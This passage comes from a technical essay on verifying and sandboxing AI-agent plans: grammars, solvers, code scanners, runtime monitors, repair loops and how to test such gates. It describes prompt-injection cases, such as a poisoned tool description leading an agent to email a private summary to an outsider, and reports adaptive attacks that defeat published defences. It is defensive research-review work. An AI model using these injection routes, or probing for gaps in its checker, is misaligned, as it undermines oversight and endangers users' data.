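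A grammar usually determines which tokens are acceptable. For Michelle's agent, it could allow only the names of installed tools, each with the right number and kind of arguments, so the model couldn't invent a tool called `fetch_email`. This grammar would still allow the poisoned plan, which uses real tools with well-formed arguments. A narrower grammar could prevent the leak by leaving out `send_email` when the user asks only for a summary, but someone would have to decide which tools each request needs.

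An ordinary grammar can't easily express rules that connect one argument to another. *Specification-Guided Generation for Large Language Models* (Previti, Vandikas and colleagues, 2026) uses a solver to recalculate the allowed values before each choice. In its example, a model configures a laptop in which an i7 processor requires at least 16 GB of memory, and that much memory requires the extended battery. Once the model picks the i7, the solver removes 8 GB from the memory options. After the model chooses the memory, only one battery remains, so the system fills it in without running the model.

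Every finished configuration obeys the rules, but an early choice can exclude something the user wanted, such as the standard battery. A second version asks the model whether any remaining value suits the request and, if none does, goes back and changes earlier choices. The method could also keep a refund's amount and payment method consistent with the order. It works on a fixed list of fields, so it suits single tool calls better than plans with loops.

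Type-constrained decoding covers whole programs. A value's type is its kind, such as number or string, and a typed language rejects a call whose arguments have the wrong types. *Type-Constrained Code Generation with Language Models* (Mündler, He and colleagues, 2025) presents a system for TypeScript that accepts a token only if the code so far can still be completed as a correctly typed program. An ordinary compiler can't check this because it rejects unfinished programs.

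The system reads the code character by character and records which variables exist, their types, and the type required at the current position. Suppose the model has written `parseInt(num`, where `num` is a number but `parseInt` takes a string. The system searches a graph whose nodes are types and edges are operations that turn one type into another. It finds that `num.toString()` is a string, so it accepts `.toString()` as the next piece of code and rejects `, 10)`.

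Testing the whole vocabulary at every step took so long that every program exceeded a five-minute limit. The system therefore picks a token first, tests only that one, and picks again if that token fails. With the smallest model, the first pick passed 99.4% of the time.

The researchers tested six open-weight models on two sets of programming tasks, HumanEval and MBPP. When the models wrote programs from descriptions, type constraints reduced compile errors by 74.8% on HumanEval and 56.0% on MBPP. Perfect syntax checking would have reduced them by only 9.0% and 4.8%. Generation took 39.1% and 52.1% longer on average. The researchers used the constraints only in a second attempt at programs that had failed to compile, so the extra attempt may explain some of the improvement. The number of programs that passed their tests rose by only 3.5%, partly because most programs already compiled.

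Blocking the model's preferred token can also lead it to write odd code. In one task, CodeLlama 34B tried to use a `.sort` operation that didn't exist. The system blocked it and steered the model to `.toString`, after which the model kept adding operations and never finished the program.

Types can express some policies, although a compile error isn't in itself a policy violation. An operator could give mailbox text the type `PrivateText` and allow only `PublicText` in messages to outsiders. If no operation converts `PrivateText` to `PublicText`, the model can't complete a call that leaks the mailbox. As with taint analysis, this depends on the tool contracts, because a tool that summarizes mailbox text must also return `PrivateText`.

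### Solvers and scanners during generation

*AGDecode* (Maghera, Arya and colleagues, 2026) runs the solver Z3 while a model writes C programs, to prevent errors such as division by zero. If the model writes `16 / num` and no earlier code rules out `num` being zero, no later line can fix the error, so the system can block the division.

Each Z3 query had a five-second limit. The median query took only one or two milliseconds when Z3 found a violation, but one to two seconds when it found none. The latter median varied with how randomly the model picked its tokens. Between 21.7% and 25.4% of all queries reached the time limit, and these timeouts alone added more than a second to the average query time.

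Half-written expressions caused most of the timeouts. After `arr[i`, Z3 has to consider every expression that starts with `i`. Once the model has finished the statement, the index may be just `i`, which makes the query easy. The researchers therefore find checking at the end of each statement more practical than checking at every token.

In the experiment, the model kept writing after a timeout, and a later query checked the whole text again. A gate can also let the model continue while nothing is running, as long as it accepts the finished plan only after a definite proof. But the prototype could not backtrack, and when a later query failed, any token written since the last successful check could have been the cause.

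Agent-C, a system Kamath, Zhang and colleagues (2025) present in *Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents*, uses an SMT solver to check one tool call at a time. It tests whether adding the call to the record of earlier calls would break a rule, such as a requirement to authenticate a customer before looking up an order. With open-weight models, it can go back and change a single argument. Providers of closed models don't share probabilities for every token, so with those models Agent-C requests the whole call again.

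With Agent-C, GPT-5 completed 70.6% of customer-service tasks within the rules, up from 66.1%, and Claude Sonnet 4.5 completed 75.2%, up from 71.8%. No violations remained, as expected, since Agent-C blocks every call that breaks its specification. But it is a runtime monitor, so earlier calls have already run when it checks the next one.

*Static Analysis Guidance for Secure LLM Code Generation* (Lunghi, Djire et al., 2026) describes a system that runs Semgrep after each finished line of Python. In one version, an alert deletes the flagged line and everything after it, and the model continues with the alert added to its instructions. On tasks chosen because scanners tend to flag the solutions, the share of DeepSeek-V4.1-flash's programs that worked and were secure rose from 52.5% to 64.4%, but two older Qwen models didn't improve. DeepSeek reached 63.5% when it criticized its own code without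 a scanner, though it used more than ten times as many tokens. Scanning every line slowed DeepSeek by a factor of 3.4 to 9.6 across the benchmarks.

CodeShield scans finished blocks of code in two stages. It is part of LlamaFirewall, Meta's open-source set of safeguards for agents, which Chennabasappa, Nikolaidis and colleagues (2025) describe in *LlamaFirewall*. The first stage relies mainly on pattern matching, takes about 60 milliseconds and is enough for about 90% of inputs at Meta. If it finds something suspicious, CodeShield runs a more thorough analysis, which averages about 300 milliseconds.

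On a hand-labelled set of model-written code, 96% of CodeShield's warnings were correct (its precision), and it caught 79% of the insecure examples (its recall). The thorough stage can't catch insecure code that the quick stage passes, because that code never reaches it. *SPLASH* (2026) adds that static analysers are good at finding dangerous code that is present, but that a missing check often leaves no pattern to match. CodeShield checks for insecure programming, such as building a database command from a visitor's input, but emailing Eve a summary is ordinary code, so a gate would need its own rules for tool calls.

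### How often each check can run

Suppose a model writes 50 tokens a second, so a ten-line plan of 200 tokens takes four seconds. The table assumes a fixed, illustrative time for each check, using CodeShield's figure for the scan and Maghera and colleagues' time limit for the Z3 query.

| Check | Time per check | At every token | At every line | Once at the end |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Simple grammar check | 0.1 ms | 0.02 s | 0.001 s | 0.0001 s |
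| Quick pattern scan | 60 ms | 12 s | 0.6 s | 0.06 s |
| Hard Z3 query | 5 s | 17 min | 50 s | 5 s |
| CodeQL build and query | 10 s | 33 min | 100 s | 10 s |

The model writes a token every 20 milliseconds, so only the grammar check is fast enough to run at every token. Running CodeQL that often would turn a four-second wait into more than half an hour. Most of those runs would also be useless, because CodeQL would have to build a database from a half-written line. The best arrangement is probably a grammar check at every token, a quick scan or small taint check at every line, and the slow checks once at the end. The final check should cover every rule again, since earlier checks may have timed out or relied on less information.

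A rejected plan is guaranteed to have no effects only if nothing runs until the gate has accepted the whole plan. A framework could save time by starting each tool as soon as the model has written the call, but with the five-line plan, it would pay Acme at line 2, before the model writes the leak at line 4. The gate would then reject the plan, but the money would be gone and the request for approval would never run. Checking each line before running it wouldn't help, because line 2 breaks no rule when the model writes it.

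Tools that only read data are less risky to start, but their results must stay hidden from the model until it has finished the plan. Some reads also have side effects. For example, fetching a web page sends its address to a server, and that address can contain private data.

### Repairing a rejected plan

After a rejection, the gate can return the plan to the model with a counterexample and let it try again, as Nikolaou and Eckhoff do in CaMeLoT. Useful feedback names the broken rule, the step that breaks it, and a case in which this happens. For the mailbox rule, the case could be the route from `fetch_mail` to the message body, and for a $500 spending cap, a balance of $501. Since no tool has run yet, the feedback contains no text from Michelle's emails. But a poisoned tool description is still in the model's input, so the model may write the same leak again. Removing the suspicious tool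 and starting over is safer than asking for another repair.

Lunghi and colleagues found that feedback helped most when the model could fix the problem locally, for instance by replacing an unsafe XML parser. The Qwen models often broke the program when the fix required restructuring it. Lowering a payment to the cap is a local fix, but adding an approval and handling a refusal may change the rest of the plan.

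A model can also follow the feedback at the expense of the task. One benchmark required each program to accept connections from other machines, which a Semgrep rule flags. The models removed the required setting in 79 of 83 cases, even though their instructions gave the task priority. A repaired plan could pass by leaving out part of the task, so the gate should check that the plan still does what the user asked, or show the plan to the user.

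There is no established limit on repair attempts. Lunghi and colleagues allowed five rollbacks per program, and Winston and colleagues' airline agent could revise its plan three times. Two or three attempts seem reasonable for a short plan. The limit should apply to the user's whole request, because otherwise an agent could get around it by submitting a new plan after each failure.

Sometimes the gate should stop sooner. If the model submits the same plan again, more feedback is unlikely to help. If the code breaks the same rule twice, an early decision may be the cause, so Lunghi and colleagues' system then restarts from the beginning. If the request itself conflicts with the policy, as when Bob's address appears only in an untrusted channel, the user should decide how to proceed. If the checker times out, the model can try a simpler version, such as one without a loop.

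When the repair attempts run out, the gate must not run any of the code. In Lunghi and colleagues' experiment, the model could finish the program with the scanner switched off, which is acceptable in a benchmark but would make a gate pointless.

### The risk of repeated attempts

Each additional unsafe plan a model submits raises the chance that an imperfect checker will wrongly accept at least one. Suppose a model submits five unsafe plans and the checker has an independent 2% chance of wrongly accepting each. The chance that it accepts at least one is 1 − 0.98⁵, or about 9.6%. With ten unsafe plans, the chance is about 18.3%.

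CodeShield, a less accurate checker, missed 21% of the insecure examples in its test. At that rate, if a model made five insecure attempts, there would be a 69% chance that at least one passed. Chennabasappa and colleagues give an example in which a coding agent rewrites a database query until CodeShield accepts it. They claim that unsafe code never gets through, but CodeShield's 79% recall doesn't support this.

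Real attempts aren't independent. If the model barely changes its plan, the checker will probably reject it again for the same reason, so the true risk may be lower than 9.6%. But feedback can also raise the risk by steering the model toward violations the checker misses. Suppose a CodeQL query catches a direct leak but misses one that passes through the note-taking tool. After a rejection, the model might switch to that route, and the loop would stop because the new plan passes the check. This could happen even if the model didn't intend to deceive.

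Lunghi and colleagues' results show that passing a scanner can differ from being secure. With Semgrep's feedback, the share of DeepSeek's programs that worked and raised no alert rose 47 points, from 10.0% to 57.1%, but the share that worked and were secure rose only 12 points. False alarms explain part of the difference, because about half of the working programs that the scanners originally flagged were already secure. A language model judged whether programs were secure, a question on which two human experts agreed only 66% of the time.

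If a checker is sound for the rule and its model of the tools is right, 500 attempts are as safe as one. But if the note-taking tool's contract doesn't state that saved text can be read back, even a sound checker will accept a leak through a note, and the model writing the code is more likely to find this gap with more attempts. An operator should therefore limit attempts even with a sound checker, and have someone review any plan that passes after several rejections under the same rule.

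## Running the approved plan in a sandbox

Before accepting a plan, the gate checks a model made up of the plan's steps, the tool contracts and the policy. When the plan runs, the interpreter, libraries or tools may do something that the model leaves out. A sandbox limits the damage by restricting what the running code can reach.

Tools are a likely place for such a gap because outsiders often write them. Adam, Lu and colleagues (2026), in *Towards Practically-Secure Tools for AI Agents*, give the example of a tool that writes a file, as described, but also sends the size of the text to a metrics service. If the tool's contract mentioned only the file, the gate would miss the network call.

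### Where to run the plan

The safest option is an interpreter for a small plan language, such as Meijer's JSON. The interpreter can call a listed tool, store a result and return a value, but it has no code for opening a file or a network connection. Even a plan that the checker wrongly accepts can therefore call only the listed tools. However, if one of those tools runs shell commands, the plan can reach everything the shell can.

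Restricted Python is full Python with some features removed. Removing enough of them is hard because Python's objects link to one another. A program without `import` or `open` can sometimes still reach dangerous functions through the attributes of harmless values.

*STELP* (Shinde, Wadhwa and colleagues, 2026) describes a system from the bank Capital One that uses a list of permitted features instead. The system parses model-written Python into a syntax tree and compares the tree with the permitted grammar, packages, functions and tools. It then runs each part of the tree through its own functions, which add further checks, time limits and retries.

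The researchers tested STELP on 164 harmless programs and 470 programs to which a model had added dangerous code, such as an infinite loop. STELP blocked all the dangerous programs and allowed 98.1% of the harmless ones. CodeShield, Meta's scanner, blocked 68% of the dangerous programs and allowed 93% of the harmless ones. But the researchers built STELP's list from the permissions that these same harmless programs needed, so the test favours STELP. A new plan may well need a function that isn't on the list. STELP added a median of 0.19 milliseconds to the running time, and 520 milliseconds in the worst case.

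STELP can't replace a gate. In one of its own examples, a plan searches Wikipedia, adds something to a database and then tries to open a network socket. STELP blocks the socket call only when execution reaches it, after the database call has run.

clauz3's runner is weaker still. It checks the source code and removes many built-in functions, but clauz3's project page warns that it "is not a hardened Python or OS sandbox". The software around the agent must also prevent it from running code in any way other than through the `clauz3` command.

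The remaining option is to allow a full language and put a boundary around the whole process. WebAssembly is a compact instruction format. Its runtime gives each program its own memory and lets it call only the outside functions that the host supplies. Containers, such as Docker's, restrict which files and networks a process can reach, but they share the host's kernel, the core of its operating system. A virtual machine has its own kernel, but it uses more memory and usually starts more slowly. These boundaries can fail too. *Containment Verification* (Moon and Varshney, 2026) cites a recently disclosed Linux kernel flaw that had existed for nearly a decade.

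| Where the plan runs | What a wrongly accepted plan can reach | What else must fail before it reaches the host |
|---|---|---|
| Small plan language | The listed tools | The interpreter or a tool |
| Restricted Python | The listed tools and anything the restrictions miss | Nothing, once the restrictions have failed |
| WebAssembly | The listed tools and the functions the host supplies | The WebAssembly runtime |
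| Container | The listed tools and everything inside the container | The shared kernel |
| Virtual machine | The listed tools and everything inside the machine | The software that separates the machines |

Every sandbox in the table lets the plan call the listed tools. If the checker wrongly accepts a plan that emails Michelle's summary to Eve, even a virtual machine won't stop the leak, because plans may use `send_email`. A sandbox only prevents code from going around the tools. For short plans, the best choice is probably a small interpreter inside a container, so that a bug in the interpreter doesn't expose the whole computer.

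A boundary around all the tools is also a crude way to control them. Adam and colleagues replayed three recorded coding sessions, each in a version the user wanted and a version with a harmful side effect. A sandbox around the whole tool server blocked a settings file change that the user had requested, but let through both a metrics report and the upload of a secret key.

Their own system analyses each tool's source code for effects and puts a small sandbox around every file or network operation. Each call has its own policy, so a tool may write to the settings file in one call but not in the next. The system gave the right result in all six cases, but that is a very small number. The experiment also assumed that the right policy was already available, and the prototype works only with Rust tools whose developers have added the sandboxes.

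### From approval to the first call

A careful interpreter could run an approved plan like this:

```
expected = hash(plan, policy, contracts, tool versions)
if the approval is missing, expired, used or for another hash: stop
mark the approval as used
for step in plan:
    args = values of the step's references
    if a precondition or a remaining policy check fails: stop
    write "started" in the journal
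    result = tool_layer.call(step, args, approval)
    write "finished" in the journal
    if the tool's postcondition fails: stop
```

A hash is a short fingerprint that changes if anyone alters the data. It has to cover the spending policy and the tools as well as the plan. If a company lowers its spending cap from $500 to $50 after the gate accepts a $500 payment, an approval tied only to the plan would still let the payment through. An updated tool could also have an effect that isn't listed in its old contract. Marking the approval as used stops an agent from running the same payment twice.

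clauz3 implements part of this. Its `run` command proves the program, sends it to an approval service and starts it only when a receipt comes back. The tools don't yet check the receipt, so code that reaches them by another route doesn't need one. clauz3's developers also plan to sign the tool files, which would show whether anyone had changed them. For tools on someone else's server, Adam and colleagues propose remote attestation, in which special hardware certifies that the server is running the code that the analysis covered.

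Passwords and payment keys should stay in the tool layer, the process that performs the calls, so that a plan that escapes its Python restrictions has none to steal. STELP sends every tool call through a separate proxy. FORGE, a runtime monitor originally called PCAS in *Policy Compiler for Secure Agentic Systems* (Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues, 2026), can add a credential to a web request after approving it. An escaped plan could still send calls to the tool layer, so the tool layer should check that each call is the next step of an approved plan.

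The postcondition check catches some tools that don't behave as their contracts state. If `delete_file("foo.txt")` also removes `notes.txt`, the later steps rest on a false assumption, and the interpreter should stop. But the interpreter can't check every postcondition. For instance, it can't determine from a mail tool's result whether the tool sent a hidden copy elsewhere.

### When the facts change after the check

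Suppose Michelle asks the agent to add a summary of her emails to a shared document, and the policy allows this only if every reader works for the company:

```
9:00  The gate looks up the readers, finds three colleagues
      and accepts the plan.
9:05  A colleague shares the document with an outside lawyer.
9:10  Michelle approves the plan.
9:11  The plan adds the summary, and the lawyer can read it.
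```

The plan, the policy and the tools haven't changed since 9:00, so the hash still matches. Security engineers call this a time-of-check to time-of-use flaw.

If the interpreter looks up the readers again at 9:11, it finds the lawyer and stops. A fraction of a second still separates this lookup from the write. The document service can close that gap if it supports conditional writes. The tool sends the version number of the reader list with the summary, and the service rejects the write if the list has changed. Neither measure helps if the colleague shares the document at 9:15. To prevent that, the company has to restrict sharing of the document.

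Lilienthal and Hong (2025), in *Mind the Gap*, examined 66 AgentDojo tasks that need at least two tool calls and judged that 56 could have a flaw of this kind. They also fused pairs of tools so that one call performs both the check and the action. In the chat tasks, this reduced the average gap between the two from 1.70 seconds to 0.07, because the model no longer had to read the first result before requesting the second call. An interpreter that runs a finished plan should get most of this benefit without fused tools. But planning first creates a longer gap, since the gate's check may be minutes old when the user approves the plan.

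Lilienthal and Hong had a model label risky pairs of tools from their descriptions, but the resulting detector found at most 25% of the vulnerable sequences, so it is probably better for the person who writes a tool's contract to mark which facts can change. There is little other research on the problem, and the survey *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents* (2026) lists only two papers. *Atomicity for Agents* (2026) studies a gap within a single step, in which a web page changes after a browser agent picks a button but before it clicks.

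### Checks that must remain at run time

Meijer compares the checks that remain after verification to array bounds checks in Java and .NET. The bytecode verifier can't check an index that a program calculates from data it receives while running, so the runtime tests the index at each access. Together, the two checks guarantee that a program never reads past the end of an array, although it may stop with an error.

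A gate can offer the same kind of guarantee. If a plan takes a recipient from an email, the gate can accept the plan on condition that, just before sending, the interpreter checks that the address belongs to a colleague and stops the plan if it doesn't. The interpreter also has to check facts that other people can change, such as who can read a document, and limits that span several plans, such as a daily spending cap.

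Designers leave some checks to run time by choice. Java lets a program treat an array of strings as an array of general objects, then checks the type of each value the program stores in it. Meijer describes this as trading formal correctness for simplicity. A gate's designer can make the same trade by leaving a complicated rule to the interpreter, but more plans will then stop partway. It helps to run these checks before the plan changes anything. If the airline's plan checks the refund amount before it cancels the booking, a bad amount stops the plan while the customer still has a seat.

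FORGE handles runtime rules that depend on what has happened so far. Like AgentArmor, it keeps a graph of what may have influenced each action, but it assumes that a model's output depends on everything the model read. A reference monitor, a component that every action has to pass through, then applies rules written in Datalog, a logic language. One rule is:

```
Deny(a) :- ExternalSend(a), Tainted(a), HasSecret(a).
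```

This rule blocks an action that sends something outside if the action depends on both untrusted input and secret data. For example, an agent that has read a vendor's document and then a confidential file can't email an outsider. The monitor decides only after the graph contains everything the action depends on. In a customer-service test, its median decision took less than a millisecond.

Palumbo and colleagues tested FORGE on AgentDojo with GPT-4o. Rules about the source of each argument reduced the rate of successful attacks from 14.1% to 0.9%, but also lowered completion of harmless tasks from 83.7% to 62.5%. A stricter policy, which blocks important actions once the agent has read any untrusted text, reduced successful attacks to 0.6% and task completion to 33.2%. This agent had no verified plan, so the figures don't show how much a monitor would add when the plan has already passed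 a check.

FORGE's guarantee assumes that the monitor intercepts every relevant action before it takes effect and that the recorded facts are true. clauz3's documentation calls such assumptions an environment contract. FORGE intercepts the tool calls of several agent frameworks and web requests made through two common Python libraries. A program that opens its own network socket bypasses the monitor, but a container without direct network access would block such connections. The agent's final answer also bypassed the monitor in the AgentDojo test. FORGE had blocked the calls in most of the attacks that the benchmark still counted as successful, and the rest worked through the final answer.

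### Verifying the agent framework

An agent framework is the ordinary software that turns a model's output into actions. Moon and Varshney used Dafny to verify a very small one, PocketFlow. Their proof represents the model as a function with no body, which may return any action the framework's interface can express. Dafny has to show that the framework enforces the policy whatever this function returns, so the result doesn't depend on the model's training or goals.

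The policy lets the agent read only files in its workspace folder, call only listed tools and take no more than a fixed number of steps. These rules are much simpler than the mailbox rule because they don't track where data came from. If `send_email` is a listed tool, the verified framework would still carry out a leak. The proof therefore complements the gate, which checks what the plan does with its tools. An interpreter for JSON plans is also small, so it would be a good candidate for a similar proof.

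The guarantee covers only effects that pass through the verified interface. It does not cover flaws in Python, the operating system or the hardware, so Moon and Varshney recommend running the framework inside a sandbox. The interface also has to be narrow. If it includes a general command for running shell code, the proof shows little about what that code will do.

Language models wrote the specifications and proofs, and one test exposed a weakness in this method. The template for the safety rules had no field for what the agent did. A model that could see the agent's code left the nearest field empty, so the rule about that field was true only because there was nothing to check. The specification still passed all three of the researchers' quality checks. An operator should therefore test that each rule can reject something, as with the mailbox rule.

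### When a verified plan stops halfway

A plan that obeys every rule can still stop halfway because a tool fails, a runtime check fails or the computer crashes. If the airline's plan cancels a booking and the payment service then goes down, the customer again has neither a seat nor a refund. Meijer lists "eliminating the need for rollbacks" among the advantages of verification, but he means rollbacks after a security breach, and a gate does prevent many of those. clauz3's documentation calls execution "all-or-nothing", but this is true only of the decision to start the program.

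Adam and colleagues suggest treating all the calls for one request as a transaction, so that either every change takes effect or none does. This is feasible for files, since their prototype already runs shell commands in a temporary copy of the file system and checks the changes when each command ends. A payment to another company is much harder to hold back. The planner can reduce the problem by putting easily reversed steps first and emails last.

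For other steps, the tool contract can name a compensating action, such as rebooking after a cancellation. This isn't a true undo, because someone else may have taken the seat. The compensating action can also fail, so the last resort should be a support ticket for staff.

The gate can check for these provisions in advance. It would assume that every tool call may succeed or fail, and require each path to end in an acceptable state. For the airline, a path with a cancellation would have to end with a refund, a new booking or an open ticket. If a plan ignored a failed refund, the gate would reject it before the cancellation. The plan language would need branches for failures, which Meijer's straight-line JSON lacks.

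A timeout is harder to handle than a clear failure because the interpreter can't tell whether the call took effect. STELP can retry failed calls automatically. This is fine for a search, but retrying a refund could pay it twice. To prevent this, many payment services accept an idempotency key, a unique label for each request. If the interpreter repeats a request with the same key, the service returns the first result and doesn't pay again. Without such a key, the interpreter should start from the last unfinished step in the journal and check whether the refund went through before trying again.

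Retries can also break a limit that the gate has proved. clauz3 can prove that a program calls `send_email` at most once, but if the tool layer repeats the call after a timeout, the recipient may get two messages. The tool layer should therefore retry a call that changes something only if the contract states that repeating it is harmless.

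## Testing the gate and finding what it misses

Meijer prefers proofs to tests because a test can reveal harmful behaviour but can't show that none exists. His gate still needs testing because its proofs don't cover mistakes in the policy, the tool contracts or the checker.

### What to measure

An operator needs several measures, because a useless gate can score well on any one of them:

| Measure | What to count | A useless gate that scores well |
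|---|---|---|
| Unsafe plans accepted | Share of rule-breaking plans that the gate accepts | One that rejects everything |
| Safe plans rejected | Share of rule-abiding plans that the gate rejects | One that accepts everything |
| Tasks completed | Share of requests the agent carries out correctly, with and without attacks | One that accepts everything, if the model resists the test attacks |
| Rules covered | Share of the company's written rules that the gate enforces | One that enforces a wrong version of every rule |
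| Time and cost | Added delay, extra model calls and questions to the user | One that skips its slow checks |

*Defending against Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks via Reasoning-enabled Task Alignment* (2026) counts an attacked run as useful only if the agent completes the user's task. AgentArmor fails this measure whenever it abandons a task to stop an attack.

Most published tests count how often attacks on the whole agent succeed, which mixes the effect of the defence with that of the model. Narisetty, Kore and colleagues (2026), in *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents*, attacked a small model, Qwen2.5-7B, on AgentDojo's office tasks. No attack succeeded even without a defence, so any defence would have had a perfect security score on those tasks. In the run they examined, the model read the injected instruction but answered the user's question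 instead.

A model may also refuse an injected instruction because it recognizes the action as harmful. To rule this out, Kurakin, Karande and colleagues (2026) used injections for harmless calls unrelated to the user's task in *Scaling Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks with Agent Swarms*. In one scenario, the result of booking a tutoring session contains an instruction to record health measurements. Such injections would suit tests of a gate whose policy limits each plan to what the user asked for, but a gate without that rule would be right to accept the call.

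The simplest way to test the gate separately from the model is to give the gate plans directly. A tester can collect plans that completed real tasks and make an unsafe copy of each by changing one detail, such as replacing the recipient or removing an approval. The gate should accept the original and reject the copy. If it rejects both, rejecting the copy isn't evidence that the rule works. The test set should also include plans that break written rules the gate doesn't enforce, so that these count as misses.

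### A day with ten unsafe plans

Suppose a gate receives 10,000 plans a day, and 10 of them are unsafe. It catches 90% of the unsafe plans and wrongly rejects 1% of the others:

| | Rejected | Accepted | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Unsafe plans | 9 | 1 | 10 |
| Safe plans | about 100 | about 9,890 | 9,990 |
| All plans | about 109 | about 9,891 | 10,000 |

Only 9 of the 109 rejections, about 8%, are right. If half the plans were unsafe, as in some test sets, 99% of the same gate's rejections would be right. An operator should therefore measure the two error rates on test plans, then combine them with an estimate of how many real plans are unsafe to work out the daily numbers.

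Reducing false alarms raises the share of rejections that are correct much more than catching the last unsafe plan does. If the gate caught all ten unsafe plans, 10 of 110 rejections would be correct. If it still caught nine but wrongly rejected only 0.1% of safe plans, there would be about 19 rejections, and nearly half would be correct. The missed plan still matters, because missing one a day adds up to 365 a year.

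The effect of a false alarm depends on whether the planner or a person handles it. If the planner can repair the plan, the user may only wait a few seconds longer. If a person reviews 109 rejections a day at three minutes each, the work takes more than five hours, and about eleven in twelve of the rejected plans turn out to be safe. Reviewers could easily start to approve plans without looking, as users do with permission prompts.

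An average false-alarm rate of 1% can also mean that the gate blocks every legitimate request of one kind. If 1% of requests ask the agent to forward an invoice to an outside accountant, a rule that blocks all of them and nothing else produces that rate. The operator should therefore count false alarms separately for each kind of task.

### What 100 failed attacks show

Suppose testers make 100 independent attacks and none succeeds. If each attack has a probability p of success, the chance of this result is (1 − p)¹⁰⁰. The upper limit at 95% confidence is the value of p that makes this chance 5%:

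```
(1 − p)^100 = 0.05
p = 1 − 0.05^(1/100) ≈ 0.0295
```

The test is therefore compatible with a true success rate of almost 3%. At that rate, an attacker with 50 independent attempts would have a 78% chance of succeeding at least once. The upper limit on the true rate is roughly 3 divided by the number of failed attacks, so it takes about 3,000 failures to bring it down to 0.1%. The 720 failed attempts against Anthropic's newest models are likewise compatible with a true rate as high as about 0.4%.

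The calculation assumes that the attacks are independent and resemble those the agent will meet later. A deterministic gate always gives the same verdict for the same plan, policy and contracts. If 100 differently worded tool descriptions lead the model to write the same plan, they test the gate only once.

Real attackers also learn from failure, which the formula doesn't allow for. A static attacker writes the injection in advance without testing it on the target, while an adaptive attacker changes the attack after seeing how the system responds. After a hundred failures, an adaptive attacker may know how to succeed on the next attempt.

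Narisetty and colleagues cite adaptive tests of Claude Opus 4.5, an older model, on coding tasks. Attacks succeeded 4.7% of the time with one attempt, 33.6% with ten and 63.0% with a hundred. If each attempt had independently had a 4.7% chance of success, the rates would have been 38% with ten and 99% with a hundred. Attacks probably failed almost every time on some targets and succeeded quickly on others. The single-attempt rate is therefore a poor guide to what a persistent attacker can do, even when extrapolating from it doesn't understate the risk.

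### Tests with attackers who adapt

In *The Attacker Moves Second* (2025), Nasr, Carlini and colleagues bypassed 12 defences against prompt injection and jailbreaks, which are attempts by users to get around a model's own safeguards. Their attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the defences, although the designers of most had reported attack success rates near zero. Some defences add reminders or markings to the prompt, some train the model on known attacks, and others use filters to detect attacks.

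On AgentDojo, the benchmark's fixed attacks succeeded as little as 1% of the time against two prompt-based defences, but adaptive attacks succeeded more than 95% of the time. Nasr and colleagues also held a contest with over 500 participants, who succeeded in every scenario, although the fixed attacks had succeeded in none.

Some designers now test their own defences against adaptive attacks. *PromptArmor* (2025) describes a detector tested against a program that uses feedback to improve its attacks. The paper reports false positives, false negatives, task completion and attack success together, which makes a bad trade-off hard to miss. All the error rates stayed low, but the designers ran the test themselves and used only one attack program. Given the results for the other 12 defences, it makes sense to wait for outsiders to test this one too.

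In 2026, Kurakin and colleagues at Google DeepMind tested how well models themselves resist injected instructions. By then, attacks from a public contest succeeded less than 1% of the time against recent Gemini models and some Claude models. The researchers used a group of cooperating AI agents to search for new attacks on several open-weight models and four Gemini models, with Gemini's external protections switched off. Even the most robust models followed injected instructions when the attacking agents were strong enough, and every model's resistance fell as the attackers improved. A good test result may therefore not last, because attackers will have better models next year.

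Narisetty and colleagues' test of Progent comes closest to testing a plan gate. Progent applies deterministic rules that a language model writes for each request and can update during a run. The adaptive attack aimed to make that model permit the harmful call. Across three sets of AgentDojo tasks, attacks succeeded 25.8% of the time without Progent. With Progent, the standard attack succeeded 4.2% of the time and the adaptive attack 2.6%.

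This is encouraging but weak evidence. The adaptive attack disguised its instruction as a routine step, which probably made the agent less likely to follow it. The researchers used one small model, one attack template and eight user tasks from each set. They work for a company that builds similar defences, and nobody has peer-reviewed the results. With Progent, the agent also completed fewer tasks under attack, down from 45.2% to 27.1%, and needed about 15 times as many model calls.

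None of these tests covers a gate that checks a whole plan before it runs. An attacker facing such a gate can try to get a harmful step into the plan through a tool description, or look for harm that an accepted plan already allows. An adaptive test should therefore give testers the policy and the tool contracts, and let them search for accepted plans that break the intended rule.

Testers need a way to recognize a violation without relying on the gate. They could put an invented fact in a test mailbox, run each accepted plan in an isolated copy of the system, and look for that fact in everything that leaves the copy. A person may have to check the summaries, since the fact could appear in different words.

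### Harms that a valid proof permits

A gate accepts plans that break the intended policy when its rules are wrong or its checker misses a data flow. Other harms can occur even when the rules match the company's intentions and the checker is sound.

Planning first can stop the leak, but the compliance notice could still make the summarizing model omit the notice from Michelle's summary. Another email could make the model report that tomorrow's meeting with the securities lawyers is cancelled, so Michelle would miss it.

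Meijer concedes that no policy can require every answer to be safe. In the talk that AI Engineer transcribed, he says it is impossible to prove formally that an answer is safe, because safety in this sense is "not a mathematical property". He worries less about text than about tool calls because a person has to act on the text before it does harm. Here that person is Michelle, who has no reason to doubt the summary.

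A stronger policy can still limit the damage. It could require a separate summarizing call for each email, so an email can distort only its own summary. Ordinary code could also list every sender and subject next to the summaries, which would expose a missing message. Michelle still has to read the original email for anything important.

An agent can also choose the wrong person from the permitted recipients. Suppose Michelle asks it to send a deal summary to Anna, and the company has two Annas. The agent picks the one in marketing, who knows nothing about the deal. Her address has the company's domain, so the mailbox rule allows the message. A stricter policy could permit only people on the deal team, if the company keeps such a list. A lookup that finds two Annas could also stop and prompt Michelle to choose. Human review works well here, because Michelle would probably notice the mistake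 if she saw the recipient's full name and department.

Permitted calls can reveal private information through their timing or number. Suppose a plan fetches a share price from an outside website, summarizes Michelle's mail and then fetches an exchange rate from the same site. Neither request contains private data, but the site's owner can time the gap between them and estimate how much mail she has. The number of calls can also reveal something about her mail, as with the loop that sends one fixed message per email. A person who reviews these calls will probably see nothing wrong.

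A policy could require all outside requests to come before the first private read, or require the same number of requests on every path. The interpreter could also send requests at fixed times. These measures slow the agent down and rule out some useful plans, so they are probably worth using only when even a small clue, such as whether a merger is under way, would be valuable.

Two plans that are harmless separately can reveal private information together. Suppose a company lets its agent share average salaries for groups of at least five people. On Monday, a plan sends a consultant the average for a team of ten, which is $80,000. On Tuesday, another plan sends the average for the nine members other than Bob, which is $78,000. Both plans obey the rule, but the consultant can subtract 9 × $78,000 from 10 × $80,000 and learn that Bob earns $98,000.

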